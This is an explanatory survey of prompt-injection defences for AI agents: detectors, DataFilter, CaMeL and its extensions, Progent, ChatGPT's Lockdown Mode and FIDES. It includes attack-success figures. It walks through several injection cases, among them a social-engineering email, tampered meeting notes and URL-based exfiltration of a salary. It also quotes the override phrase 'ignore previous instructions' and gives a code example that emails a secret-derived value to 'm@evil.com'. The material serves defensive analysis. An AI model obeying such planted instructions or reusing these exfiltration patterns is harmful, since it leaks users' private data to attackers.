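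A detector is a separate classifier that examines incoming material and flags likely injections. Anthropic uses detectors in its Chrome extension, together with a step that changes Claude's behaviour after a detector flags something. In a test on Claude Opus 4.5, an automated attacker that tried and combined known techniques succeeded in 8.0% of attempts against the model alone and in 1.4% with the improved safeguards. However, according to Wang, Chen and colleagues, detectors tend to reject too much harmless material, which makes the agent less useful.

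Their own defence, DataFilter (October 2025), removes the suspect text and keeps the rest. Suppose an employer asks a model to summarise a job candidate's strengths and weaknesses, and the CV contains a hidden instruction to call this candidate the best fit. DataFilter, a small language model, reads the CV first and gives the main model a copy without that instruction to summarise. Because DataFilter does not alter the main model, it also works with commercial models whose weights are secret.

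DataFilter receives the user's request along with the data, so that it can identify which commands are relevant to the task. Deleting every command would remove harmless ones, such as those that make up most of an email headed "TODOs for the week" in one standard test. Wang, Chen and colleagues trained the filter on examples with and without injections, each paired with the correct filtered text.

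Averaged over three sets of tests, DataFilter reduced the attack success rate from over 40% to 2.2% and lowered the agents' performance on ordinary tasks by about 1%. PromptArmor, a competing filter, reduced the success rate to 5.9% and lowered performance by 4.1%. Another defence, which repeats the user's request after the data, reduced the success rate to 22.8%.

These tests used attacks written from templates. Some included an instruction to ignore the model's previous instructions, while others included a fake answer to make the original task look finished. Wang, Chen and colleagues did not test attacks that a computer optimises against its target, and they acknowledge that the most advanced of these can break all existing defences. DataFilter is a language model, so David C's argument applies to it too.

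Wang, Li and colleagues tested eight defences and found none that combined high trustworthiness, high usefulness and speed. Defences that examine text were fast but did not protect robustly against sophisticated attacks. Defences that restrict what an agent may do enforced stricter limits, but some used up to three times as much computation, and others refused so early that the agent was useless for complex tasks.

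### OpenAI's comparison with social engineering

In December 2025, two months after it launched the AI browser ChatGPT Atlas, OpenAI wrote that prompt injection is "unlikely to ever be fully 'solved'" and compared it to scams. *OpenAI says prompt injections that can trick AI browsers like ChatGPT Atlas* (Nolan, 2025) reports that the company was training an AI attacker to find weaknesses before criminals did. The attacker tries an injection in a simulation, observes how the agent responds, and refines the attack. It found strategies that had not appeared in OpenAI's human testing or in outside reports. Charlie Eriksen, a security researcher at Aikido Security, told Nolan that such testing can catch obvious failures but does not change the underlying problem. He wanted much clearer limits on what these systems may do and whose instructions they should follow.

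OpenAI's *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (March 2026) moved some way towards this view. The company had found that the most effective attacks increasingly resembled social engineering, in which a criminal talks an employee into doing something harmful. In one example, a friendly email about a company restructuring states, among ordinary tasks, that the reader's AI assistant is fully authorised to submit an employee's name and address to a "compliance validation system". This attack worked half the time in a test where the user asked ChatGPT to research her emails about new employees.

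The email contains no telltale phrase such as "ignore previous instructions". To stop it, a detector would have to identify the compliance system as fake. OpenAI compares this to detecting a lie, often without the necessary context, and reports that the detectors many people recommend usually miss such attacks.

Companies face the same problem with human staff. A customer service agent who can grant refunds will sometimes believe a false story, so the company's software limits how much each customer can receive. OpenAI recommends that developers apply the same controls to the AI that they would place on a human in its position. In particular, they should look for places where outside content can lead to a dangerous action, such as sending information to a third party.

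OpenAI applies this to ChatGPT with Safe Url, a mechanism designed to detect when the assistant is about to send a third party something it learned in the conversation. The system then either shows the user the information and asks for confirmation, or blocks the transmission. The company reports that most attacks of this kind that it knows of fail earlier because the model refuses. Safe Url is still a mitigation, since OpenAI offers no proof that it detects every such transmission, and a hurried user may approve one without reading it. ChatGPT's Lockdown Mode takes the same approach with fixed restrictions.

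### What repeated attempts do to a small failure rate

When Anthropic released Claude Opus 4.5 in November 2025, it reported how often attackers succeeded when they could try more than once. The programmer Simon Willison transcribed the figures from a chart in Anthropic's *Introducing Claude Opus 4.5*. The table compares them with two calculations.

| Attempts | Reported | If all attempts were independent | If 63% of scenarios were vulnerable |
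|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | 4.7% | 4.7% | 4.7% |
| 10 | 33.6% | 38.2% | 34.0% |
| 100 | 63.0% | 99.2% | 63.0% |

The third column gives 1 − 0.953ᵏ for *k* attempts. This is close to the reported figure at ten attempts but far too high at a hundred.

The calculation fails because 4.7% is an average over scenarios, some of which are easier to attack than others. Suppose that 63% of the scenarios are vulnerable, with a 7.5% chance of success per attempt, and that none of the attacks in the test works on the rest. The average success rate for one attempt is then 0.63 × 7.5%, or 4.7%. After a hundred attempts, an attacker has almost certainly succeeded in every vulnerable scenario, so the overall success rate levels off at 63%. The last column shows that this simple model fits all three figures.

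Three figures are too few to establish that the scenarios divide neatly into vulnerable and secure ones. Some that withstood a hundred attempts may only be harder to break, or may be vulnerable to an attack outside the collection. The lower total also doesn't help a user whose task is among the vulnerable ones, because an attacker who makes a hundred attempts will almost certainly succeed.

The 63% also probably overstates the risk from hidden instructions in email. Gray Swan, which ran the test, measured injections in outside material both separately and combined with jailbreaks and other attacks by the user, and the chart seems to show the combined result. Anthropic's system card for Claude Opus 4.6 (February 2026) reports that injections in outside material had a success rate of only 16.5% against Opus 4.5 after a hundred attempts. That figure includes corrections to grading errors, which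 may explain part of the difference.

Anthropic has since retired this test because its newer models had reached or nearly reached the best possible score. The replacement has 28 scenarios and 1,130 attacks, and builds on a public competition described by Dziemian, Lin and colleagues (2026). In the system card for Claude Opus 5 (July 2026), Anthropic reports that attackers succeeded against that model 0.2% of the time with one attempt and 2.0% with fifteen. For OpenAI's GPT 5.6 Sol, the figures were 3.1% and 20.0%. If the attempts were independent, the rates after fifteen would have been about 3% and 38%, so the same gap appears here.

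These figures are not directly comparable with those for Opus 4.5 because the scenarios and attacks are different. On the new test, Opus 4.8, which came before Opus 5, had a rate of 5.5% after fifteen attempts, and Opus 5 cut that by more than half. Newer models have followed, including Claude Mythos 5.2, which Mowshowitz (2026) reviewed in November in *Fable and Mythos 5.2*.

### Fixed attacks and adaptive ones

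Both tests use a fixed collection of attacks, which is a serious limitation because most of the twelve published defences that Nasr and colleagues examined in October 2025 failed against adaptive attackers. Ma and colleagues have since tested ten defences with AutoDojo, a program that revises its injections according to which ones succeed. PIGuard, an injection detector, stopped all the fixed attacks on one model but let through 28.0% of the adaptive ones. Five defences had stopped almost all the fixed attacks on that model, but only Progent, which restricts the tools an agent may use, held up against the adaptive ones.

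The attack success rate rose even more in Anthropic's own tests. In 2025, an automated attacker called Shade made 200 attempts per scenario to hijack Claude Opus 4.5 while it operated a computer, and never succeeded when the model used extended thinking, a mode in which it reasons before acting. That result depended on the attacker. Anthropic and Gray Swan then obtained a stronger version of Shade, which succeeded against the same model in the same mode in 28.0% of single attempts, and at least once within 200 attempts in 78.6% of the scenarios.

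A test with fixed attacks can therefore show that a defence is weak, but a good score is only evidence about attacks like those in the test. Such tests are still useful for checking that an update has not reintroduced an old vulnerability, and for comparing models if none of them was used to produce the attacks. Anthropic warns, for instance, that the new test's results for Gemini 3.1 Pro are not directly comparable, because competitors had used that model to find the attacks.

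The results of adaptive tests also depend on the attacker. In the coding test for Opus 5, Shade had developed its attacks against earlier models, and Anthropic then tried them on Opus 5. Only 0.56% of attempts succeeded, but at least one succeeded in 13 of the 40 scenarios. With probes that inspect material before the model acts on it, the figures fell to 0.18% of attempts and 4 scenarios. An attacker who developed attacks against Opus 5 itself might do better.

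Anthropic replies that its tests are in some ways harsher than real conditions, because the attacker can practise on the exact scenarios and try many times. A criminal usually does not know how a company has set up its agent, and each failed attempt may alert someone. This is a fair point about an attack on one company, but it is less reassuring for a popular product, which a criminal can buy and practise on privately.

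### When a small failure rate is acceptable

An attack that rarely works on any one user can still benefit the attacker. If a malicious web page succeeds against 0.2% of agents and 100,000 agents read it, it hijacks 200 of them on average. Anthropic wrote in 2025 that a 1% success rate "still represents meaningful risk".

The risk depends as much on what a hijacked agent can do as on how often attacks succeed. Suppose a shop's AI can grant refunds and ordinary software caps them at $50 per customer. If 1,000 customers try to trick it and 2% succeed, the shop loses at most $1,000. It can compare that sum with the cost of human staff, who also make mistakes, and decide that the risk is worth taking. Without the cap, the shop could not put an upper limit on its loss, however small the failure rate. A small failure rate is also easier to accept when the operator can reverse the damage, or notice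 failed attempts and stop the attacker before one succeeds.

By these standards, an agent that summarises public web pages without access to any accounts can tolerate occasional failures, because the worst likely result is a misleading summary. One successful attack on the email assistant, however, can irreversibly leak years of confidential mail. Willison (2025) argues in *Claude Opus 4.5, and why evaluating new LLMs is increasingly difficult* that developers should assume that a sufficiently motivated attacker will find a way to trick the model, and design their applications accordingly.

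Several layers of protection can make failures much rarer. Anthropic's auto mode combines probes on incoming material with a classifier that blocks dangerous actions. In a browser test with 129 scenarios and ten attempts at each, no attack succeeded against Opus 5 or Claude Mythos 5 with this combination. Without it, 3.7% of attempts succeeded against Opus 5 and 29.7% against Mythos 5.

Even if the 129 scenarios were a random sample of what users encounter, up to 2.3% of all scenarios could still be vulnerable, at 95% confidence. Anthropic describes the two layers as failing independently, but that may not hold for an attack like the restructuring email, which makes both the incoming text and the resulting action look like routine office work.

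David C recommends a rule that Simon Willison and Baibhav Bista arrived at in an online discussion. When a model reads material from someone, its permissions should drop to that person's. A stranger who emails the user has no right to forward the user's mail, so an assistant that has read the stranger's email should not be able to forward it either. Ordinary software can enforce this without recognising the attack. But applied strictly, the rule would also stop the assistant from answering a supplier's question with information from another email, and tasks like this are much of what people want from an assistant. CaMeL, from researchers at Google and ETH Zurich, is designed to keep more of that usefulness while still limiting what hidden instructions can do.

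## CaMeL: an agent whose plan hidden instructions cannot change

An ordinary agent chooses each action after reading the results of the last one, so instructions hidden in those results can change what it does next. CaMeL (short for "capabilities for machine learning") makes the agent plan its actions before it reads anything an attacker could have written. Debenedetti, Tramèr and colleagues published the design in March 2025 in *Defeating Prompt Injections by Design*. CaMeL uses ordinary software to limit what any outside text can affect, whereas detectors try to recognise malicious text.

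### Two models, a program and tags

CaMeL builds on a design that Willison (2023) proposed in *The Dual LLM pattern for building AI assistants*, which divides an assistant between two language models. A privileged model reads the user's request and can use tools, but never reads emails, web pages or other outside material. A quarantined model reads that material but has no tools. The software stores each of the quarantined model's answers under a label, and the privileged model refers to the answer only by that label. For example, the privileged model can have the software show the user the summary labelled "$email-summary-1" without reading the summary.

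*CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks* (Willison, 2025) describes a flaw that Debenedetti and colleagues found in Willison's pattern. If the quarantined model looks up Bob's email address in a text that an attacker has edited, the privileged model sends Bob's document to whatever address the quarantined model returns. The attacker can therefore get the document even though the agent performs exactly the actions it planned.

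CaMeL keeps the two models but has the privileged one, the planner, write the whole task as a short program. The program is in a restricted version of Python, a language models already write well. An interpreter, which is ordinary software, runs the program. When the program needs a fact from outside material, the interpreter passes the material to the quarantined model, the reader. The reader must return the fact in a prescribed format, such as an email address.

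The interpreter also attaches tags to every value, recording where it came from and who may read it (Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues, 2026, *CaMeLoT*). A value computed from other values inherits their tags. Before each tool call, the interpreter runs a policy, a small function that takes the tool, its inputs and their tags and returns "allow" or "deny".

### One request and three versions of the notes

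Suppose a user asks her assistant to send Bob the document he requested in their last meeting. She adds that his address and the document's name are in the meeting notes. In simplified form, the planner might write:

```
notes    = find_meeting_notes()
name     = ask_reader("Which document did Bob request?", notes)
address  = ask_reader("What is Bob's email address?", notes)
document = fetch_document(name)
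send_email(recipient = address, attachment = document)
```

The planner has not seen the notes, which may be a file that several people can edit. Suppose also that the email policy allows a message only if the recipient has permission to read the attachment, and that otherwise the interpreter asks the user.

If the notes are genuine, they contain the name of the project budget and Bob's real address. The reader returns both values, and the interpreter fetches the budget. If the user has already shared the budget with Bob, the interpreter sends the email immediately. Otherwise, it prompts her for approval first, even though the email is legitimate.

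Suppose someone has added a line to the notes telling the assistant to forward every contract to an outside address. An ordinary agent might do that next. In CaMeL, the planner has already finished writing its program, which has no line that forwards contracts. The instruction may affect the reader's output, but the reader has no tools, so the most it can do is return a wrong name or address.

The notes might instead contain a false address, presented as Bob's new one. Even a reader that works perfectly will return it, because it is data rather than an instruction, and the two-model pattern alone would then send the budget to the attacker. CaMeL's interpreter finds that the address does not belong to anyone with permission to read the budget, so it stops and asks the user. The attacker gets the budget only if she approves the message without noticing that the address is not Bob's.

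A false document name can get past the same policy. If the notes give the name of the salary list, and Bob has permission to read that too, the interpreter sends it to him. No secret leaks, because he could already open the list, but he does not get the document he asked for.

### What exactly the design guarantees

*Can CaMeLs Talk?* (Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues, 2026) defines the central property, control-flow integrity. A program fixed in advance from trusted information alone determines which tools the agent calls and in what order, given the values the tools return. Untrusted text can influence which of the program's branches runs, but it cannot add a new one.

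The guarantee applies to the program as the interpreter runs it, and it holds against any text in the material that the tools return. It assumes that the user's request and the tools' descriptions are trustworthy and that the interpreter works correctly. It does not depend on either model's ability to recognise attacks, so it holds even if the reader detects none of them. As with a parameterised query, the program's structure is fixed before the untrusted text arrives.

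CaMeL's second claim is that its tags and policies control where information goes. This is harder to establish, and Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026) point out in *The LLMbda Calculus* that CaMeL has no theorem to support it. Debenedetti and colleagues themselves call formalisation a "crucial direction" for further work. CaMeL's control of information is therefore still a mitigation, although its fixed plan comes close to a guarantee.

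CaMeL's plan can change when a program fails, because CaMeL then lets the planner try again using error messages that can depend on untrusted text. CaMeL censors these messages to limit the attacker's influence, but Garby and colleagues note that the censorship has no formal guarantees. A system that never retries, like the one Peters-Gill and colleagues built, avoids this problem but fails tasks that a second attempt might have completed.

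The assumption that the user's request is trustworthy can also fail. Tallam and Miller (2025), in *Operationalizing CaMeL*, warn that an attacker may use phishing or other deception to get instructions into the request. The planner would then treat them as the user's own.

### False text and plans that are too general

A fixed plan does not make the agent's answers true. If the user asks for a summary of an email, the attacker can distort the summary or add an instruction to phone a fraudulent number. Narisetty, Kore and colleagues (2026) note in *Adaptive Evaluation of Out-of-Band Defenses Against Prompt Injection in LLM Agents* that Debenedetti and colleagues explicitly exclude such harms from what CaMeL is meant to prevent.

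A plan can also be so general that preventing changes to it gives little protection. Garby and colleagues ran CaMeL on a task in which the user asks the agent to read a file and follow its instructions precisely. In some runs, the planner wrote a loop that could call any of the tools, depending on the file's contents. Anyone who could edit the file could then direct the agent without changing its program. With CaMeL's policies switched off, attacks succeeded this way in two runs.

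### Leaks that the tags miss

The tags can fail to follow a secret. Garby and colleagues adapt a classic example from computer security, which in simplified form looks like this:

```
rich = True
tmp  = True
if balance > 1000000: tmp = False
if tmp: rich = False
if rich: send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

The balance is secret, and the policy forbids sending anything that depends on it. If the balance is above a million, the third line sets `tmp` to False, and the interpreter tags `tmp` as secret. The program then skips the assignment on the fourth line, so `rich` stays True and still counts as public, and the policy allows the email. If the balance is lower, `rich` becomes False and no email goes out. The recipient therefore learns whether the balance exceeds a million. This leak occurs because the interpreter updates tags only on the branch it takes, even though skipping a branch also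 reveals information about the balance.

An attacker cannot insert these lines, because the planner writes the program without reading the attacker's text. The leak occurs only if a user's ordinary request happens to produce a program of this shape. The example is therefore better evidence that the tags are unsound than that the leak is easy to exploit. Garby and colleagues also found a more mundane fault. When a program inserts an untrusted value into a longer text, as planners often do to build messages, the result can count as trusted.

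Other leaks, called side channels, come from what an outsider can observe of a program's behavior. If a program fetches a web page a secret number of times, the site's owner can learn the number by counting the visits. An error can reveal whether a secret meets some condition. The retry loop makes this worse because each attempt can reveal one yes-or-no fact, and 20 such facts can identify one number among about a million. According to Narisetty and colleagues, the CaMeL paper demonstrates two working side channels.

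### Who writes the policies

Someone also has to write the policies and keep them up to date. The policies must be strict enough to keep secrets from leaking without repeatedly interrupting the user. Willison, who has worked in application security for two decades, says he has trouble thinking through such policies himself. He also worries that people asked to approve too many actions will start saying yes to everything. His example is the security researcher Troy Hunt, who fell for a phishing attack while jet-lagged.

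Policies written for one set of tools do not carry over easily to another. *Evolution Under Fire* (2026) left CaMeL out of one of its two comparisons partly because CaMeL's policies were specific to a benchmark, and Ma and colleagues left it out of a test for a similar reason. A company that wants to use CaMeL would likewise have to write policies for each new tool.

### What the protection costs

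The main evidence on how CaMeL affects task completion and token use comes from AgentDojo, a benchmark with 97 tasks in simulated office work, banking, travel and the messaging service Slack. Narisetty and colleagues report that CaMeL, using OpenAI's o3 model, solved 77% of the tasks, compared with 84% for an undefended agent. CaMeL used 2.82 times as many input tokens and 2.73 times as many output tokens.

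The first version of the CaMeL paper reported 67%, which Tallam and Miller cite. OpenAI released o3 in April 2025, a month after that version, so the 77% must come from later runs. A stronger model probably explains at least part of the increase, though the revision may have changed other things.

Two attacks succeeded in CaMeL's own evaluation, as Garby and colleagues describe. In one, the user asked the agent to pay a bill according to a file that the attacker had written. Debenedetti and colleagues place this attack outside CaMeL's threat model. In the other, the agent only quoted a hotel review word for word, but the benchmark's automatic check counted this as obeying the review.

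The overall figures combine the effects of the fixed plan and the policies on task completion. To separate the two, Garby and colleagues ran CaMeL on the 16 banking tasks, three times each, with two newer models. With the policies off, it completed 67% of attempts with one model and 71% with the other. With the policies on, it completed 37.5% with both. With only 16 tasks, the margins of error are over 20 percentage points, but the drop is large.

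The policies added little measurable security. Attacks succeeded in 5 of the 622 attacked runs that finished with the policies off, and in none of 588 with them on. But two-thirds of the combinations of task and attack required an action that the plan would never contain, so the fixed plan alone could stop them. The policies matter most against false values, which this set of attacks tests less thoroughly. A deployed system could ask the user to approve some of the blocked payments, which would let more tasks succeed but interrupt the user more often.

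Garby and colleagues created an alternative, a small programming language for agents called LLMbda, and verified its interpreter with the proof checker Lean. They proved that changing hidden inputs does not alter the probabilities of what an observer sees when he is allowed to see only certain results, except by affecting whether the program finishes. The same mathematics shows that untrusted inputs cannot influence trusted results, with the same exception.

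Their agent completed 75% of the banking attempts with GPT-5.2, twice the share CaMeL completed with its policies on. Part of the difference comes from exceptions to the rules, which the planner can declare before reading anything. An exception allows an untrusted value to be used for a certain purpose, such as the amount of a payment. This weakens the protection against false values but not the protection of secrets. Without exceptions, the completion rate fell by 10 to 12 percentage points on the two models tested.

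Attacks on this agent succeeded in only 2 of 1,296 runs, and both involved the forged bill. Rules about where information came from cannot distinguish a real bill from a forged one in the same file. They can only forbid all payments based on the file, which would also stop the user from paying her real bills.

### Tasks whose next step depends on what the agent reads

A program written in advance suits tasks whose steps the planner can foresee. "Pay the bill in this file" becomes two steps, reading the file and sending the money. Li, Wen and colleagues (2026) report in *AgentDyn* that only 6 of AgentDojo's 97 tasks require an agent to revise its plan. Their own benchmark, also called AgentDyn, has 60 tasks in shopping, software projects and daily life, all of which require this. For example, a checkout page may tell the agent to log in first, which may require a code sent by email.

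CaMeL completed none of these tasks with any of the four models in Li and colleagues' main comparison. An undefended agent based on GPT-4o completed 53%. No attack succeeded against CaMeL, but that is not an achievement, since it completed no tasks.

The zero may not be entirely due to the fixed plan. Ma and colleagues count only 12 of the 60 tasks where the user leaves the action open. In another 30, the user omits details such as an amount, and in the remaining 18 the user specifies everything. A good planner might foresee a login page and write a branch for it. CaMeL also needs a description of each tool's output format, because its planner writes code to handle results it cannot see. Peters-Gill and colleagues had to add these descriptions before CaMeL could do reasonably well on their tests. If AgentDyn lacked them, some of the failures would be due to the set-up.

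Better preparation would not help with a request to do everything on a colleague's to-do list, because the planner cannot specify steps that appear only on the list. It can write a loop that carries out whatever the list contains, but then whoever edits the list controls the agent. The interpreter can require the user to confirm each step, but then she does much of the work she wanted to delegate.

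For such tasks, a mitigation may be the only practical choice. Meta SecAlign, a model trained to resist injections, completed 55% of AgentDyn's tasks, and 9.0% of attacks on it succeeded. Li and colleagues consider such training the more pragmatic approach, but a 9% attack success rate is tolerable only if a hijacked agent can do little damage.

### Plans with many branches

Researchers have since tried to extend CaMeL to less predictable tasks. *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (Foerster, Blanchard and colleagues, 2026) adapts it to agents that operate a computer by looking at the screen and clicking. The planner cannot see the screen, so it writes branches for what might be there, such as a cookie notice or a browser that is already open. At each step, the program has the reader describe the screen, checks whether an expected condition holds, and picks a branch accordingly. The plans averaged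 41 tool calls and 40 branches, compared with about 5 and 4 for AgentDojo.

Foerster and colleagues report that the system keeps up to 57% of the performance of leading models. Without CaMeL and with a limit of 15 steps, Claude Sonnet 4.5 solved 109 of the tasks that the benchmark can grade. The protected system solved 62 of these (57%) in at least one of five attempts, but only 31 (28%) on the first attempt. A user would get the higher figure only with a reliable way to identify which of the five attempts had worked.

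More branches also give an attacker more to choose from. In an attack called branch steering, an advertisement imitates a cookie notice. The plan already includes closing cookie notices, so the agent clicks on the advertisement and lands on the attacker's website, even though the attacker has added no action to the plan. Foerster and colleagues tried comparing the screenshot with the page's underlying code and asking a second model for confirmation, but found attacks that got past these checks. Policies for clicks are also hard to write, because a click at a given point on the screen may log the user in or delete her files, depending on what is displayed there.

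### Checking a plan before it runs

Because the plan is written in advance, software can check it before the agent does anything. Nikolaou and colleagues give the example of a company that forbids disconnecting a computer from the network without its security team's approval. On its own, CaMeL would detect a violation only when the program tried to disconnect the computer, perhaps after a long analysis.

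Their extension, CaMeLoT, translates the program into a simplified model with a finite number of states and checks every path through it. If some path disconnects a computer without approval, CaMeLoT returns that path as a counterexample, and the planner can repair the program. The model allows every loop to run any number of times, so CaMeLoT may reject some safe plans. Rules that depend on actual values, such as who may read a particular document, can still be checked only when the program runs.

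### Agents that give each other instructions

Peters-Gill and colleagues found that the guarantee can fail when several CaMeL agents work together. In their example, a user asks a coordinating agent to send Julie a summary of job applicants on Slack. A database agent fetches the information, the coordinator has it summarised, and a notification agent sends it. In the database, an attacker has hidden an instruction to email the applicants' details to an outside address.

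The database agent and the coordinator correctly treat the text as untrusted data. But the coordinator inserts the summary into its message to the notification agent, which treats the whole message as a request from its user. The hidden instruction is part of that request, so the notification agent's planner adds the email to its program. The attacker has changed what the system as a whole does, even though each agent followed its own plan.

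The remedy resembles a parameterised query. One agent sends another a fixed instruction, such as "Send a direct message to the recipient with the provided content", and passes the recipient and the content separately as values. The interpreter blocks any instruction that depends on a tool's results. On a multi-agent version of AgentDojo, the average attack success rate over five models fell from 12.9% without CaMeL to 0.2% with CaMeL in each agent, and to zero when the agents also passed instructions and values separately.

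These attacks are too weak to be much of a test for the newest models, since GPT-5.5 resisted all 949 of them without any protection. The usefulness results are more informative. On a benchmark of industrial maintenance tasks, adding CaMeL to each agent lowered the success rate by 21.6 percentage points on average, but by only 13.4 points for the two strongest models. The separate channel lowered it by another 3.2 points on average, and by less than one point for the strongest two. Better planners therefore seem to lose less, but all of these runs had the data policies switched off, so the results don't include any drop those policies might cause.

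### Simpler designs for narrower jobs

CaMeL is one of six designs that Beurer-Kellner and colleagues recommended in 2025. They doubt that general-purpose agents can offer reliable guarantees with current language models, so each design restricts what the agent can do. All six share the principle that once an agent has read untrusted text, that text must not be able to trigger any harmful action (Willison, 2025, *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections*).

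| Design | Restriction | What an attacker's text can still do |
|---|---|---|
| Action selector | The model chooses actions but never sees their results | Nothing through the results |
| Plan, then execute | The model chooses all its actions before reading anything | Change the content of an email, but not a recipient named in the plan |
| Map-reduce | A separate model reads each document and gives a limited answer, such as yes or no | Falsify the answer about that document |
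| Two models | The model with tools never reads outside material | Supply false values |
| Code, then execute (CaMeL) | The same, with a program and tags | Supply false values that the policies allow |
| Context minimisation | The software removes the user's message before the model writes its answer | Influence the database search, but not the wording of the answer |

The simplest designs sacrifice little when the job is narrow. An assistant that only directs customers to the right help page can use the action selector, because it never needs to read the page. An assistant that sorts invoices can use map-reduce, and the most a forged file can do is get itself included. CaMeL's extra complexity is justified when an agent has to combine information from several sources and then act on it.

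### Progent and its adaptive test

CaMeL requires developers to rebuild their agent around the interpreter, while Progent, a related system, can be added to an existing agent. In Progent, a language model uses the user's request to write rules for which tools the agent may call and with what inputs. Ordinary software then checks every call against these rules. The checks are deterministic, but they depend on rules that a language model wrote. In Progent's default configuration, the model can also loosen the rules after reading the results of tool calls, so an attacker could plant instructions in those results to try to make it do so.

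Progent withstood the adaptive attacks by Ma and colleagues. In June 2026, Narisetty and colleagues attacked it differently, disguising the malicious action as a routine step the user had already authorised and hoping the model would loosen the rules to permit it. They also ran a standard attack for comparison.

| | No defence, standard attack | Progent, standard attack | Progent, adaptive attack |
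|---|---|---|---|
| Banking: attack success | 19.0% | 1.9% | 3.7% |
| Slack: attack success | 58.3% | 10.8% | 4.2% |
| Office work: attack success | 0.0% | 0.0% | 0.0% |
| Mean attack success | 25.8% | 4.2% | 2.6% |
| Mean tasks completed | 45.2% | 27.1% | 25.8% |

The test was small, with eight user tasks from each of three areas, each run three times. The agent was Qwen2.5-7B, a model of about 7 billion parameters that is far weaker than those in current products. The office tasks can't be used to judge Progent, because no attack on them succeeded even without it. Excluding those tasks, the mean attack success rates are about 39%, 6% and 4%.

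Adapting an attack to Progent may still help an attacker, despite the lower success rate under the adaptive attack. Narisetty and colleagues suspect that the polite disguise also made the attack less persuasive to the agent. On the banking tasks, where the disguise seems to have weakened the attack less, the success rate rose from 1.9% to 3.7%, though the numbers are too small to establish a real increase. The researchers call their results preliminary. They tried only one attack template and did not optimise its wording automatically. They work for LaunchSafe, which builds security tools on the same principle as Progent.

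With Progent, the share of tasks completed under attack fell from 45% to 27%, and the agent needed about 15 times as many model calls per task. On AgentDyn, which has longer tasks, agents using Progent completed between 3% and 25% of tasks, depending on the model, because Progent had trouble setting suitable permissions when there were many tools to choose from.

Narisetty and colleagues have not yet tested an attack that uses only the actions the rules permit. Progent checks a call's tool and inputs but does not track where the inputs came from. If a user asks the agent to pay a bill, the rules have to allow a payment, and they may allow one to a forged account number on the bill.

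## Lockdown Mode and FIDES: fixed restrictions in products

OpenAI's Lockdown Mode for ChatGPT applies restrictions that the company chose in advance, whatever the user asks, whereas Progent has a language model write new rules for every request. OpenAI introduced the mode in February 2026 for businesses, schools and healthcare organisations, and extended it to personal accounts in June. OpenAI's *Introducing Lockdown Mode and Elevated Risk labels in ChatGPT* (2026) describes it as an optional setting for a small group of people, such as executives and security teams at prominent organisations. OpenAI says most users do not need it.

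### What Lockdown Mode switches off

OpenAI's help page *Lockdown Mode* lists what changes when a user turns the setting on. Agent mode stops working, and so does deep research, in which ChatGPT investigates a question across many web pages. ChatGPT no longer retrieves images from the web or downloads files to analyse. Users can't give code written in Canvas, ChatGPT's editing workspace, access to the network. They can still upload files and generate images, and ChatGPT's memory works as before.

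Most of these features can send a request to a computer outside OpenAI, and even a request to fetch something can carry data. Suppose an attacker uses hidden text to tell ChatGPT to open a page on the attacker's website, with the user's salary at the end of the address. The attacker's server receives the salary as part of the request, whether or not the page exists. Loading an image from an address the attacker chose can send data in the same way.

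Lockdown Mode therefore lets ChatGPT browse only pages that OpenAI has already stored, so that no live request leaves the company's network. A web address made up to leak a salary has no stored copy, so the attacker's server never receives the salary. This restriction also means that search results may be old or missing.

### Three conditions for data theft

Willison (2025), in *The lethal trifecta for AI agents*, argues that an attacker can easily steal data through an agent that combines three things: access to private data, exposure to text the attacker can write, and a way to send data out. If the agent has no access to private data, there is nothing to steal. If it reads nothing from outsiders, the attacker cannot give it instructions, and if it has no way to send data out, the data stays in the conversation.

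Removing any one of the three prevents the theft, but what the user loses depends on which one is removed. An assistant without private data can't answer questions about her own mail. An assistant that reads nothing from outsiders can't open most of that mail, or the web. An assistant that can't send anything can still read her mail, summarise it and draft replies, though she has to press "send" herself. Willison (2026), in *OpenAI Help*, calls the ability to send data out "by far the easiest leg to restrict" without making the system far less useful. Companies had already been restricting it case by case. He lists more than a dozen products with such leaks since 2023, and writes that the vendors fixed almost all of them promptly, usually by blocking the route the data took out.

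The argument is weaker for agents whose job is to send information. A booking agent that cannot contact a hotel is useless. It is also hard to list every way data can leave. Willison himself calls these routes almost limitless, since a request to another program, an image or a link the user clicks can carry data. Closing one route may barely limit the agent, but the defender has to find them all.

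He is more worried about people who assemble their own agents. The Model Context Protocol (MCP), a standard for connecting language models to tools, encourages users to combine tools from different suppliers. One tool may read private files, another may read public web pages, and a third may send messages. Even if each supplier has secured its own product, none controls the combination.

### What the software enforces and what OpenAI promises

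OpenAI describes the restrictions as deterministic. Hidden text can't make ChatGPT open a live web page, because the model doesn't control whether that is allowed. Willison considers this the crucial feature, since a sufficiently devious attack could manipulate a model that did control it. But users have to trust that OpenAI implemented the restriction correctly, because they can't inspect the service's code.

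Even if ChatGPT makes no live browsing requests, data can leave in other ways, and OpenAI explicitly declines to guarantee that none will. It warns that data may still get out through apps connected to ChatGPT, unforeseen combinations of features or new techniques. The Hacker News' *Researchers Bypass ChatGPT Lockdown Mode to Exfiltrate Chats Without User Interaction* (2026) reports that the security company Check Point found a way for data to leave through another feature of the app, and that OpenAI fixed the flaw on 18 September. The flaw was in ordinary software around the model, so training the model to resist injections would not have removed it.

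Connected apps are the largest exception that OpenAI allows on purpose. On personal accounts, Lockdown Mode blocks apps from accessing outside services live or changing anything in them when this would conflict with its protections. In organisation-managed workspaces, it does not automatically disable every app, because some essential work depends on them. Administrators choose which apps and actions to allow. OpenAI advises them against allowing write actions unless they can confirm that a malicious outsider won't see the result. Two organisations that both use Lockdown Mode can therefore have quite different protection.

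Lockdown Mode also leaves the network access of Codex, OpenAI's coding agent, unchanged. A programmer who turns on Lockdown Mode to protect a confidential project still has to restrict Codex separately, for example with a list of permitted websites.

Lockdown Mode also does not keep malicious text away from the model. A stored web page or an uploaded file can still contain an injection, and OpenAI acknowledges that the injection can make an answer wrong.

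Willison concludes from the existence of Lockdown Mode that ChatGPT's default settings do not robustly protect data against a determined attacker. OpenAI's security chief, Dane Stuckey, says that the loss of functionality is worthwhile for people at elevated risk but that the mode is not meant for everyone. OpenAI did not include adoption figures in its announcement.

### FIDES puts labels on data

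Microsoft's FIDES (Flow Integrity Deterministic Enforcement System) lets an agent keep its ability to send data out, but is designed to prevent any single action from combining that ability with private data and untrusted text. Microsoft researchers described the design in 2025, and the company released it in May 2026 as an experimental part of Agent Framework, its toolkit for building agents.

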